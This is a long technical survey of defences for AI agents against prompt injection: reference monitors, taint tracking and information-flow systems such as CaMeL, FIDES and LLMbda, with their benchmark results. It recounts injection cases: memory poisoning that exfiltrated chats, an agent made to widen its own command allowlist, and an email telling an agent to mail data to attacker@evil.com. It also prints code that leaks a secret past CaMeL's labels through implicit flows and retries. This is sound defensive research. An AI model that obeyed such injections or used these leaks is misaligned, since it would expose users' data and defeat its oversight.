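ChatGPT's "Memories" feature stores facts about the user for later conversations. An attacker could use a malicious document or website to plant instructions there through the Mac app. From then on, the app sent all of the user's conversations to the attacker, hidden in requests for an invisible image. An ordinary prompt injection usually ends with the conversation, but these instructions stayed in memory and affected later conversations too.

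Anderson required the monitor to be tamperproof, and ChatGPT's memory is not a monitor. The attack still counts as tampering because the app let the model decide what to send, and the model presumably treated its memories as the user's wishes. By writing to the memory, the attacker changed the closest thing the system had to a policy.

Christodorescu and colleagues describe a fix that checks which web addresses ChatGPT may contact. This makes it harder for stolen data to get out, but it acts only at the end of the attack. They also recommend asking the user before the app stores a memory, as some other agents do.

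Amp's case is closer to what Anderson had in mind. Amp kept a list of commands it could run without asking in a settings file that the agent could edit. An attacker could therefore inject an instruction for the agent to add a command to the list and then run it. Christodorescu and colleagues would prevent the agent from changing such files and require human approval for any edit.

Progent keeps its policy where the agent cannot edit it. But Progent has to update the policy during the task, and the model that proposes updates reads the same emails and web pages as the agent. An attacker who cannot edit the policy directly can still try to manipulate that model, as Narisetty and colleagues did. Progent reduces the opportunity by having the model decide whether an update is needed before it sees the tool's output. If the model decides that one is, it reads the output, and the only remaining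 protection against an expansion of the policy is the approver.

### A policy for each task

Anderson expected permissions to change often and planned for administrative programs to maintain them. In his design, though, somebody with authority decided what each user could do, and the system recorded the decision. Agent designers instead want software to infer permissions from a sentence in ordinary language and revise them during the task, after the agent has read text from strangers. Neither the 1972 report nor the 1975 principles explain how to do that.

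A permission for one task can be much narrower than a permission for an account. *PAuth*, by Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send $100 to Bob. Today's authorisation systems grant the agent the right to make transfers, but the request implies only the right to make that one. *PAuth* treats the request itself as the authorisation.

This works well when the request contains all the details. The request about Alice's to-do list didn't mention Slack, and the agent discovered that it needed to send Slack messages only when it read her email. A policy based on the request alone would have stopped the task there. A few steps later, following Eve's email would also have required a new permission. The solver treats both as expansions, so designers have so far left it to a person or another model to recognize that the user meant to follow Alice's instructions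 and not Eve's.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes that a policy is correct if its formal rules and the user's words lead to the same decision in every situation the agent could reach. No program can check this directly, because the words are ambiguous. If a user says "don't share anything sensitive", someone first has to define "sensitive" in terms that software can test. The paper suggests restricting how people phrase such instructions and measuring how far the formal rules might differ from the original instruction. It regards both as open research problems.

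Even under a correct policy, an agent can misuse the actions it is permitted, just as it can misuse a valid capability. The last rule in the Progent example restricts who receives the Slack message, but not its content. Shi and colleagues do not aim to prevent attacks on the content of such text, or attacks that steer an agent towards one of several legitimate choices, such as the attacker's product.

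### Better models instead of a monitor

Monitors take work to build and can stop agents from finishing their tasks, so it would be simpler to train models to ignore injected instructions. Some of Progent's own results support this view. Without a monitor, AgentDojo's attacks succeeded 39.9% of the time against GPT-4o, but only 6.8% of the time against Claude Sonnet 4, a 2025 model. The figure was 4.8% against Meta-SecAlign-70B, which Meta trained to resist injections. Developers might reasonably expect further training to make the monitor unnecessary.

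However, those figures come from a fixed set of attacks, and Nasr and colleagues broke MetaSecAlign by adapting their attacks to it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* also argues that training cannot settle what the user authorised. If the request is ambiguous, even a well-trained model has to guess, and it may guess differently when the wording changes slightly. A written policy at least records one interpretation that people can read and correct. They can also tighten the policy safely, because removing a permission never allows an action that was previously refused. By contrast, training a model to resist one attack may make it more vulnerable to another.

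The objection overstates the choice between better training and a monitor, because the two can be combined. With Progent added, attack success fell to 0.5% for Claude Sonnet 4 and 0.3% for Meta-SecAlign-70B. Better training also improves the monitor as long as models write its policies. For the same reason, a design like Progent does not fully remove the model from the trusted computing base. An attacker can no longer succeed by fooling the agent alone, but may still succeed by fooling both the policy writer and whoever approves its proposals.

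## Taint tracking and information-flow control

A reference monitor that judges each request separately cannot track data once the agent has read it. Information-flow control addresses this by labeling data, carrying the labels along when a program copies or combines it, and checking them before the data goes anywhere.

### Denning's lattice

Dorothy Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976) gave information-flow control its standard mathematical form. Systems of the time, such as Multics, controlled who could open a file but mostly relied on programs being trustworthy with the contents afterwards.

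In Denning's model, every file, variable and user has a label. An order on the labels says which may flow to which, so "public" may flow to "secret" but not the reverse. A second operation, the join (written $\sqcup$), gives the label of anything computed from several inputs. If a program computes a value from $a_1$ to $a_n$ and stores it in $b$, the flow is secure when

$$L(a_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup L(a_n) \rightarrow L(b),$$

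where $L$ is the label and the arrow means "may flow to". If the label of $b$ is fixed, the system refuses a write that breaks the rule. If the label can change, the system raises it until the rule holds.

Denning argued that the order and the join can't be arbitrary. If A may flow to B and B to C, then A must be allowed to flow to C, because a program could otherwise get around the rules by moving data from A to C through B. And if a program may store $a + b$ in $c$, it must also be allowed to store $a$ there, since it could set $b$ to zero. The join therefore has to be the lowest label to which all the inputs may flow. A lattice is an ordered set in which any two members have such a lowest upper bound and also a highest lower bound.

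Her paper covers only secrecy. Researchers later used the same structure for trust, where trusted data may flow anywhere but untrusted data may not flow into anything that has to stay trusted. Agents need both, so each label becomes a pair. Suppose the user's request is (trusted, public), the tax return is (trusted, secret) and a stranger's email is (untrusted, public). The join works on each half separately:

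| Inputs | Label of the result |
|---|---|
| Request and tax return | (trusted, secret) |
| Request and stranger's email | (untrusted, public) |
| Tax return and stranger's email | (untrusted, secret) |

The last row is the dangerous one because a message based on both the tax return and the stranger's email is too secret to send to a stranger and too untrusted to determine what the assistant does next.

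Programmers have long used a simple version of this for trust alone. Perl, a language behind many early websites, has a taint mode that marks everything a program receives from outside:

```
my $name = <STDIN>;        # typed by a visitor: tainted
my $file = "/tmp/$name";   # contains $name: tainted too
unlink $file;              # Perl stops before deleting anything
```

The programmer can remove the mark by extracting part of the text with a pattern, such as one that matches only letters and digits. Perl then treats the extracted text as safe, whether or not the pattern was sensible. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists this kind of tainting, along with prepared statements, as an established defence against SQL injection.

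### One model for tools, another for strangers' text

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, assumed that prompt injection would remain unsolved and asked what people could safely build anyway. He proposed using two models. The privileged model takes the user's request and can use tools, but never sees text from outside. The quarantined model reads that text and has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes material between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the steps are:

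1. The privileged model requests the latest email. The controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`.
2. The privileged model requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model tells the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

The privileged model sees only the variable names. In Denning's terms, the pattern has two trust labels and one rule, that untrusted text may not flow to the privileged model. Willison also applied the join without naming it. He treated the summary as tainted because the email was, and said the same of anything further models might produce from it.

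Willison called the solution "pretty bad" because it is complicated to build and a single mistake could let untrusted text reach the privileged model. It also has a flaw that he acknowledged two years later, after Google DeepMind's CaMeL paper described it. To explain CaMeL, he used the request "Send Bob the document he requested in our last meeting". Under the dual-LLM pattern, the quarantined model would read the meeting notes and extract Bob's address. An instruction hidden in the notes could make it return the attacker's address instead. The privileged model would then send the document to the attacker, even though its plan was correct.

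### Labels between planner and executor

In *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao (2024) also separated planning from reading, but used explicit labels. In their system, f-secure, a model plans one step at a time and an executor carries out each step. A security monitor labels every output with the join of its inputs' labels and shows the planner only the trusted items.

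In the first example, a user wants the manager notified if any budget in the mailbox exceeds $1,000. The search finds two budgets from colleagues, for $724 and $1,024, and an attacker's email with an instruction to send all budgets to Mallory. The user has marked colleagues as trusted. The monitor checks each email separately, so the planner sees both real budgets and notifies the manager. Willison's privileged model would have seen none of the three emails and needed the quarantined model to compare the numbers.

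In another example, the user asks the agent to append `medical.txt`, from an outside database, to the user's own `clinical.txt` and send the result to a doctor. The merged file is untrusted because one of its two sources is. The planner can still have the file sent, but it never reads the instruction hidden in it.

Wu and colleagues proved that untrusted data cannot affect the plan in their model of the system. Let $Q_1$ and $Q_2$ be two collections of data that contain the same trusted items and may differ in everything else. For any request $q$ and any plan $\pi$,

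$$\Pr[\pi \mid q, Q_1] = \Pr[\pi \mid q, Q_2].$$

They adapted this from noninterference, a property that Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined in 1982.

The tests are less informative than the proof. On InjecAgent, a benchmark of 1,054 attacks, none succeeded against f-secure, while 51.6% of the basic attacks succeeded against an unprotected agent using GPT-3.5 Turbo and 28.7% against one using GPT-4 Turbo. But Wu and colleagues labelled every tool output in this test as untrusted, so no attack reached the planner. In the usefulness tests, they labelled every tool output as trusted, so the monitor withheld nothing. Neither test measured how often an agent fails because the monitor withholds information its planner needs.

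### CaMeL

CaMeL has the privileged model write the whole plan in advance, as a program in a restricted form of Python. For the request about Bob, a simplified plan might be:

```
notes   = find_notes("last meeting")
address = quarantined_model("What is Bob's address?", notes)
title   = quarantined_model("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
send_email(to = address, attachment = open_file(title))
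```

According to Nikolaou and colleagues, CaMeL's interpreter runs the plan and tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, a policy written as an ordinary Python function checks the tool, the arguments and their tags, then allows or refuses the call. If an injection replaces Bob's address with the attacker's, the policy can refuse the call because the attacker is not among the document's permitted readers. This closes the gap in Willison's pattern, although researchers later found leaks of another kind in CaMeL.

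Deciding everything in advance works less well when the right plan depends on what the agent finds. Strict policies also block harmless work. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, put CaMeL's completion rate on AgentDojo at 67% and attribute many of the failures to treating all untrusted inputs as equally risky. The figure is hard to trace because their reference for CaMeL gives the title of a different work, on poisoning training data.

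### Why labels spread

Denning's method works well for programs because a compiler can determine which variables each line uses. The line `c := a + b` depends on `a` and `b`, so `c` gets the join of their labels. This analysis doesn't work on a model's answer, because any part of the prompt may have influenced it, so the only safe label for the answer is the join of the labels on everything in the prompt.

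An agent's prompt also keeps growing, so its label can only rise. Suppose the mail assistant opens a colleague's message giving the time of the conference dinner, then a stranger's advertisement. After that, every call it requests is labelled untrusted, including the one that tells Maria the time. If it also opens the tax return, everything it writes afterwards is labelled secret as well. After a few more steps, a strict policy would permit almost nothing.

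*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes separating the influence of different inputs on a model as an open research challenge. Some researchers try to estimate that influence. Siddiqui and colleagues (2024) look for a smaller set of messages that leads to a comparable answer, then regenerate the answer from those messages alone and label it based on them. RTBAS uses a model's internal attention patterns, or a second model as a judge, to decide which labels matter. These methods permit more actions, but an attacker may benefit when the estimate is wrong. The alternative is to keep the troublesome text out of the prompt.

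### FIDES

Microsoft's FIDES, described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), takes the second approach. It labels each message, tool call, argument and result as trusted or untrusted. Each label also lists the people who may read the data, which for an email are the sender and the recipients. When data is combined, only people who may read every source may read the result. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan another, only Bob and Carol may read a text based on both.

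When a tool returns data whose label would raise the conversation's label, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. It decides this separately for each field, so the model might see an email's date but not its subject or body. FIDES hides only data that would reduce the agent's permissions, while Willison's pattern hides all outside data.

The planning model has two ways to use hidden text. It can send a question about a variable to a quarantined model, which has no tools and must answer in a set format, such as yes or no, a choice from a list, or free text. The answer goes into a new variable. The planning model can also read a variable directly, and the conversation then takes on the variable's label.

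Before a tool runs, a policy checks the labels. For sending email, Costa and colleagues used a rule with two alternatives. If $R$ is the set of recipients and $S$ is the set of people who may read the contents, then, leaving aside an extra restriction on web links, FIDES sends the message if

$$R \subseteq S \quad \text{or the call itself is trusted.}$$

In the paper's opening example, a user asks the agent to summarise recent emails about Project X and send the summary to the user's manager. One of the emails tells the agent to ignore its instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to attacker@evil.com.

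First, suppose an agent tracks labels but hides nothing. When it reads the emails, the conversation becomes untrusted. If the model follows the attacker's instructions and requests the call, the policy blocks it because the call is untrusted and the attacker is not among the top email's readers. If the model ignores the attacker and tries to send the summary to the manager, that call is untrusted too, and the policy blocks it unless the manager was already entitled to read all of the emails.

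With FIDES, the planning model requests these calls instead:

```
read_emails(...)                                   -> #emails
query_llm("Summarise progress on Project X", #emails) -> #summary
send_email(to = manager, body = #summary)
```

The attacker's text is inside `#emails`, where the planning model cannot see it. The conversation is still trusted when the planning model requests the third call. Only the body is untrusted, which the policy allows, so the manager gets the summary. The quarantined model read the attacker's instruction, but it cannot send anything.

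The model can still write a bad summary. Costa and colleagues point out that an email could make it return an empty one. A stricter policy could require the body of the outgoing message to be trusted too, but that would block every summary of strangers' emails.

### AgentDojo with and without the policy check

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and 36 attack goals, with GPT-4o as the model. Without policy checks, they counted 152 successful attacks on a basic agent and 21 on FIDES. Hiding text was not enough by itself, because the planning model could open a variable and then obey what it found. With policy checks, no attacks succeeded against either agent. The policy thus accounts for the perfect score, and the contribution of FIDES is in how much useful work remains possible:

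| Tasks completed, no attack | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic agent, checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The spread of labels caused the basic agent's drop from 93.3% to 20.0% on Slack tasks. FIDES recovers part of the loss, and more with a better model. With OpenAI's o1 and the checks on, it completed an average of about 61% of tasks, compared with 44% for the basic agent, but was still about 23 percentage points below an unprotected agent. Costa and colleagues emphasise a gap of only 6.3 points, which they measured with the checks off, when FIDES provides no guarantees.

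Better models will not close all of that gap. In about 44% of the banking tasks, the agent must decide what to do from what it reads, for example by opening a file and following the payment instructions inside. FIDES blocks the payment once the agent has read the file. A genuine bill and a forged one have the same label, so Costa and colleagues count these failures as intended.

The zero also needs qualification. AgentDojo's scoring counted three successful attacks against FIDES with checks. Costa and colleagues excluded them after looking at each, because the benchmark counts as successful some calls that the policy had blocked and some that it had allowed as harmless. They also don't try to stop attacks that only change text, such as one that makes the agent recommend a particular hotel. They labelled as untrusted exactly the fields where AgentDojo places its attacks, but someone running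 a real agent has to decide which fields to distrust without knowing where the attacks will come from.

### Declassification and endorsement

In Denning's model, information that has reached the highest label can never move to a lower one. Wu and colleagues consider this impractical for a whole system, as did the researchers who built information-flow systems after Denning. Those researchers added two controlled exceptions: declassification, which lowers the secrecy of data, and endorsement, which raises its trust level.

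The second half of the FIDES rule for email allows declassification. Suppose the user asks the mail assistant to send a tax return to an accountant who is not one of the file's permitted readers. The tool call comes from a trusted conversation, so FIDES treats it as the user's decision and sends the file. If a stranger's email asks for the same file and the model follows that request, the call is untrusted and FIDES refuses it. Costa and colleagues identify this as "robust declassification", the principle from the early 2000s that an attacker must not be able to influence the release of secrets. Both requests use the same tool, file and credentials, so neither a permission token nor a list of allowed tools would distinguish them.

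Endorsement helps when a plan depends on untrusted text. A user might ask the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, put the meeting in the calendar. The planning model needs one fact from the emails, so it asks the quarantined model for a yes or no and reads only that answer. An attacker who wrote one of the emails may be able to control the answer but cannot fit an instruction into it. If the answer is yes, the planning model has the quarantined model extract the date and participants into a variable, then passes the variable to the calendar without reading it.

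FIDES includes the answer's format in its label so that policies can make such exceptions. A choice among $n$ options carries at most $\log_2 n$ bits, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no and reject untrusted free text. Willison had made the same exception in 2023 for answers from a fixed set of categories. But small answers can add up, and twenty yes-or-no questions give an attacker about a million combinations to choose from. Costa and colleagues left the enforced formats out of their AgentDojo tests because few of the tasks needed them, so the results above provide little evidence of how well this approach works.

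Other exceptions are riskier. Costa and colleagues mention that a system might relabel a document as trusted after a prompt injection detector has passed it, but warn that this could weaken the guarantees. The warning is justified, because Nasr and colleagues often got past such detectors. An attack that evades the detector would be labeled trusted, and every later check would accept it.

Designers can also leave the decision to the user. Tallam and Miller propose a quick confirmation before an agent uses untrusted data to change the user's own files, and multi-factor approval before it sends email or money. Willison had predicted that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible. Limiting the requests to consequential actions should help, but an assistant that mainly sends email would still need approval often.

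### What the designers cited

Most of this work openly borrows from earlier security research. Wu and colleagues cite Denning's 1976 paper, Goguen and Meseguer, and the military secrecy model of David Bell and Leonard LaPadula. One of them, Ethan Cecchetti, had published on information-flow control in 2017, so the team included someone who already knew the field. Costa and colleagues cite Denning, Goguen and Meseguer, and later work on programming languages and on TaintDroid, which tracked private data on Android phones. Nikolaou and colleagues trace CaMeL's tags to a 1977 paper by Dorothy and Peter Denning, among other sources.

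The borrowing continues in three papers from 2026. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* presents CaMeL and FIDES as extensions of classical information-flow control, for which it cites Denning. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, on privacy leaks from agents, also lists her paper in its references. *PACE* lists JFlow, a 1999 extension of Java that checks information flow, and libdft, a 2012 tool for tracking data in ordinary programs.

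Knowing the literature gave these designers security properties to work with, as well as a vocabulary. Wu and colleagues could adapt an existing definition of security and prove that their system met it. Costa and colleagues could choose explicit secrecy, a weaker property from a 2016 paper, and say exactly what it leaves out, namely anything an observer can infer from which actions the agent takes.

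Willison is the exception, because his post mentions no work on information flow, though it quotes an encyclopedia's definition of the confused deputy. He calls the quarantined model's output "tainted", a word that web programmers knew from tools like Perl's taint mode. He may therefore have picked up the idea secondhand, but the word is too common for us to be sure.

Later papers did not always cite Willison's proposal either. Seventeen months after his 2023 post, Wu and colleagues published a system that similarly separates a model that plans from components that read untrusted text. Their 55 references include Denning's 1976 paper but not Willison's post. Costa and colleagues cite both.

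## A leak known since the 1970s that returned in an agent defence

The information-flow research behind CaMeL's tags also described a way for secrets to leak despite such tags. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) showed that this leak is possible in CaMeL.

### How a bank balance loses its label

Information usually moves through a program when the program copies one value into another. It can also escape through the program's choice of branch, which researchers call an implicit flow. Suppose an agent manages a bank account and its plan contains this line:

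```
if balance > threshold: send_email(outsider, "rich!")
```

The email contains no data from the account, but the outsider who receives it learns that the balance is above the threshold. CaMeL blocks this version by applying the label of a branch's condition to everything the program does inside that branch. The condition depends on the secret balance, so the call to `send_email` counts as secret and the policy doesn't allow it.

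Two extra variables get around the check:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(outsider, "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program changes it inside a secret branch. If the program skips the branch, the label stays as it was.

| After this line | High balance: `tmp` | High balance: `rich` | Low balance: `tmp` | Low balance: `rich` |
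|---|---|---|---|---|
| `rich = True` | True, public | True, public | True, public | True, public |
| `if balance > threshold: ...` | False, **secret** | True, public | True, public | True, public |
| `if tmp: ...` | False, **secret** | True, public | True, public | False, public |
| `if rich: ...` | email sent | | no email | |

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and secret, so the program skips `rich = False` and `rich` keeps its original public label. If the balance is low, `tmp` never changes and stays public, so the program sets `rich` to false in a branch that seems to depend only on public data. Either way, `rich` ends up public, and its value shows whether the balance is above the threshold.

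The label of `tmp` is secret in one run and public in the other, so the label itself depends on the balance. Nobody can detect this from a single run, because the evidence is in an assignment the program skipped.

### From Fenton to CaMeL

Garby and colleagues trace the example to Fenton's *Memoryless Subsystems* (1974). Fenton modelled a memoryless subsystem, one that cannot pass on unauthorised information about its input, and proved the model correct. They say that Denning rewrote his example as ordinary program code in her 1976 paper on the lattice model, and that security researchers "rediscovered" it decades later. For the rediscovery they cite a 2009 paper by Thomas Austin and Cormac Flanagan on tracking information while a program runs. They offer no evidence that Austin and Flanagan reached the example independently.

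*Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977) described a remedy, which is a check that a compiler could make before a program runs. The check covers both branches of every condition. In the bank program, the compiler would find that `tmp` may change in a branch that depends on the balance, so it would require `tmp` to be secret whether or not that branch runs. `rich` depends on `tmp`, so it would have to be secret too, and the compiler would reject the email.

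Nikolaou and colleagues trace CaMeL's tags to this 1977 paper, so CaMeL's idea of labelling data came from work that had already dealt with leaks through an untaken branch. It is unclear whether CaMeL's designers knew Fenton's example.

### One bit per attempt

The other leak that Garby and colleagues found is in the ordinary Python loop around CaMeL's interpreter. If a plan fails, the loop gets a new plan from the planning model and tries again. The loop carries no labels from one attempt to the next, even though the new plan depends on how the previous one failed. CaMeL's designers acknowledged this and censored the error messages, but the fact that a plan failed still reveals information.

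Suppose the balance is a whole number of dollars below 1,024, and someone who can choose the plans wants to learn it. The first plan attempts a forbidden action only if the balance is at least 512. If the policy blocks the plan, the balance is at least 512, and otherwise it is lower. The next plan tests the midpoint of the remaining range. Ten plans reveal the exact balance, and twenty are enough for any balance up to about a million dollars.

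Most information-flow systems tolerate a leak of one bit per run, because preventing it would mean controlling whether and when every program finishes. The loop makes this leak serious by allowing repeated runs. Researchers knew about this too. Garby and colleagues cite a 2011 paper on security over multiple runs. Sands, who helped find the flaw in CaMeL, had co-written a paper 18 years earlier, in 2008, whose title states that guarantees of this kind leak "more than just a bit".

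### A language that labels every value

Garby and colleagues propose LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, as a remedy. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal notation in which programs consist of functions. Every value has a label, and every step of a program passes the labels on, including in code the model has just written.

The conversation with the model also has a label, which combines the labels of everything the program has sent. A program can fork a conversation to ask a side question and then discard the fork, or it can clear the conversation. Programmers can therefore implement Willison's two-model pattern with separate conversations, whereas CaMeL and FIDES build it into their architecture.

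LLMbda prevents implicit flows by forbidding a program to change anything public while it is in a branch that depends on a secret, a rule that Garby and colleagues credit to Austin and Flanagan. In one of their examples, a program sends the model a message saying that x is false and then, only if a secret is true, sends a second message telling it to set x to true. LLMbda stops the program at the second message. Raising the conversation's label to secret at that point would be correct for this run, but if the secret were false, the conversation would stay public and the model's answer would reveal the secret. The same rule would stop the bank program at `tmp = False`.

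Moving the retry loop into the language creates a new problem. Once a failed attempt has read untrusted data, the data's label spreads to the next plan, and the agent can no longer do anything that requires trust. Garby and colleagues solved this by having their agent, Randori, practise first. During practice, reading a file returns a fixed placeholder and sending money does nothing, so errors reveal nothing about the real account. When the plan works, the model writes a final version, which runs once on the real data. This also prevents a retry from making the same payment twice.

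### The noninterference theorem

Noninterference means that changing the secret inputs to a program makes no difference to its public results. The same definition works for trust, where changing the untrusted inputs must make no difference to the trusted results. Agents complicate this because a model's answers are partly random, so the theorem has to be about probabilities, and because a program may run forever or break a rule and stop.

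Take two starting states that differ only in data an observer is not allowed to see. Let $\mu_0(x)$ and $\mu_1(x)$ be the probabilities that the program finishes and the observer sees result $x$. The theorem says that there is a single set of probabilities $\omega$ for which

$$\mu_0(x) \le \omega(x) \quad\text{and}\quad \mu_1(x) \le \omega(x) \quad\text{for every } x, \qquad \sum_x \omega(x) \le 1.$$

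Suppose that with a low balance the agent sends a greeting 60% of the time and finishes silently 40% of the time. With a high balance, it also sends the greeting 60% of the time, but LLMbda stops it the other 40%. Setting $\omega$ to 0.6 for the greeting and 0.4 for silence satisfies the condition. If the high balance instead led to a greeting 90% of the time and silence 10% of the time, $\omega$ would have to total at least 0.9 + 0.4 = 1.3, which exceeds 1. The condition therefore allows the balance to affect whether the program finishes, but nothing else the observer sees. If the program always finishes, the two sets of probabilities must be identical.

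To prove this, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running the program, which replaces any computation on hidden data with a dummy value. This second way gives the same probabilities for both starting states because it never uses the data in which they differ. It also produces each visible result at least as often as the real program does, so its probabilities can serve as $\omega$.

Garby and colleagues derived their definition from a general method published in 2023. They then discovered, and acknowledge in the paper, that Geoffrey Smith and Rafael Alpízar had proposed essentially the same property in 2011 and had anticipated three of the results about it.

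They checked all the proofs in Lean, a language in which a computer verifies each step, and wrote LLMbda's interpreter in Lean too. The theorems therefore cover the program that actually calls the model, however the model responds. They don't cover mistakes by the developer, who must still label the data sources correctly and put checks on the sensitive tools. The theorem also allows the one-bit leak, so a user who keeps revising and rerunning a blocked task could recreate the retry loop by hand.

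### Results on the banking tasks

Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks. There are 16 tasks and nine attacks, and they ran each of the 144 combinations three times with each of three models. Two of the 1,296 attacked runs succeeded. They also reran CaMeL with two of the models:

| Tasks completed, no attack | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 64.6% |
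| Randori, unable to endorse data | not tested | 54.2% |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 66.7% | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 37.5% | 37.5% |

CaMeL completes roughly half as many tasks when its policy checks are on. Randori's checks are always on, and it does about as well as CaMeL does with its checks off. The comparison used only 16 different tasks, so the margins of error are around 20 percentage points or more either way. It also favours Randori somewhat, because Garby and colleagues gave Randori looser policies than CaMeL's and let its plans endorse untrusted data. A plan has to request endorsement before the agent reads any real data, and a second theorem shows that endorsement cannot make secrets public.

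The figure of two in 1,296 also makes the test look harder than it was. In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needed a tool that the user's task gave the plan no reason to call, so writing the plan in advance normally defeated the attack. The other 47 combinations account for 423 runs.

Both successful attacks involved the same task. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Without endorsement, LLMbda blocks this attack, but it also blocks the genuine payment.

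### Several CaMeL agents

In October 2026, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues asked in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* whether CaMeL still protects a system in which agents give tasks to other agents. Their co-author Ilia Shumailov had helped design CaMeL.

Researchers built a system with a coordinating agent, a database agent and a notification agent, each protected by CaMeL with no policies switched on. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants' details on Slack. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database to email the details to an outside address. The coordinating and database agents kept to their plans, but the coordinating agent's request to the notification agent included the summary, which contained the injected instruction. The notification agent treated the request as coming from its user, so its planning model read the instruction and added the email to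 the plan.

Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering", since data loses its untrusted status as it passes between agents. Their fix, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into a message that the receiving agent's planning model reads and a set of variables hidden from that model. The interpreter blocks any message that depends on a tool's output, and the variables keep their tags. This is close to a prepared statement, with the message as the template and the variables as the values.

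They then split AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran 949 attacks on each of five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. Without protection, 36.1% of attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1 and none against GPT-5.5, so the GPT-5.5 results can't show whether the defence stops attacks. On a separate set of industrial tasks, using CaMeL on each agent separately reduced task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by a further 3.2.

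Multi-CaMeL has no retry loop, so it avoids that leak. But it extends CaMeL's interpreter, and Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that it inherits the problem with implicit flows. The interpreter would accept a message that depended on untrusted data through a skipped branch.

They aim for control-flow integrity, a weaker guarantee than noninterference. An agent has this property if trusted input alone determines its plan. Untrusted data may still decide which branch of the plan the agent follows, because every branch was in the plan from the start. This is sensible for an assistant that has to act on what it reads. If the user says to send a reminder unless Bob has cancelled, Bob's email should affect whether the assistant sends it. Strict noninterference would forbid that unless the program endorsed his answer.

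However, control-flow integrity does not keep data secret. The bank program satisfies it, since both outcomes are in the plan, but still reveals the balance. CaMeL's policies are meant to protect secrets, but they rely on the labels that implicit flows bypass. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested no policies and leave stronger guarantees to future work.

### How serious the leaks are

With a single CaMeL agent, the bank program would be hard for an attacker to use. The planning model writes the plan before the agent reads any outside text, so an injected email normally cannot add those five lines. In Garby and colleagues' tests with policy checks on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished. But the benchmark's attacks evidently did not exploit either leak, so this result was no evidence that the leaks were absent.

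Such code can still get into a plan. In a system with several agents, boundary laundering lets an attacker's text reach a planning model. When a user asked CaMeL to follow a file's instructions precisely, its planning model sometimes wrote a plan that could call whichever tool the file named. Two attacks succeeded this way with policy checks off. A planning model could also have a hidden backdoor that makes it write the leaking code.

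An honest plan may contain the same pattern by accident, because programmers often set a default and change it later:

```
pay = True
if quarantined_model("Does this email dispute the bill?", email): pay = False
if pay: send_money(...)
```

If an attacker's email gets the answer "no", `pay` keeps its original trusted label, and nothing records that the payment depended on the email. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's interpreter treats untrusted text as trusted once a plan inserts it into a longer string. Perl's taint mode handles that case correctly. Plans routinely insert names and addresses into messages, so this fault probably matters more in practice than Fenton's example.

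### What the old proofs would have changed

CaMeL's plans suit the Dennings' method well. According to Odersky and colleagues, the plans are written in a subset of Python that does not let them define functions, which makes them easier to analyse before they run. But Nikolaou and colleagues point out that CaMeL checks plans while they run because some of the facts a policy needs are known only when the agent calls a tool. A file's permitted readers, for example, may be unknown until the agent opens it. An advance check would have to assume the worst and refuse more plans. Austin and Flanagan's rule avoids this but stops some harmless programs, including many that set a default and change it later. Either remedy might have reduced CaMeL's 37.5% completion rate further.

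Attempting a proof would have helped even without a complete remedy. Proving noninterference for CaMeL's `if` statement requires comparing a run that takes the branch with one that skips it, and the proof fails at that step. CaMeL's designers called formal treatment a "crucial direction" for later work, and Tallam and Miller asked for machine-checked noninterference proofs in May 2025. FIDES has the same gap for secrets, but Costa and colleagues disclosed it, so users can allow for it.

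Designers could also have reused existing software. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) builds on LIO, an information-flow library for the programming language Haskell, and treats Willison's two-model pattern as one use of it. An agent can keep its tools after reading untrusted text, because the library then restricts what those tools may do. Strict policies still reduced the number of AgentDojo Slack tasks the system completed, which Garby and colleagues report fell from 15 of 21 to 8. CaMeL completed 7.

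No proof of this kind would have stopped the forged payment request, because it carries the same label as a genuine one. CaMeL's designers had seen the same attack in their own tests and classed it as one that CaMeL is not meant to prevent.

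## Rules that remove an agent's permissions after it reads risky data

Tracking every value, as CaMeL and LLMbda do, requires a special interpreter or language for the agent's plans. A coarser method gives the whole program a single security level, changes that level according to what the program reads, and then treats everything the program writes as if it depended on everything it has read. This assumption is far too cautious for many ordinary programs, but it is nearly accurate for a language model, because the whole prompt may influence each answer.

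### Two water marks

Kenneth Biba, who worked on military computer security at the MITRE Corporation in the 1970s, described the rule for trust. Each program $s$ and each file $o$ has an integrity level $i$, which is higher the more people can trust it. A program that reads a less trusted file drops to that file's level:

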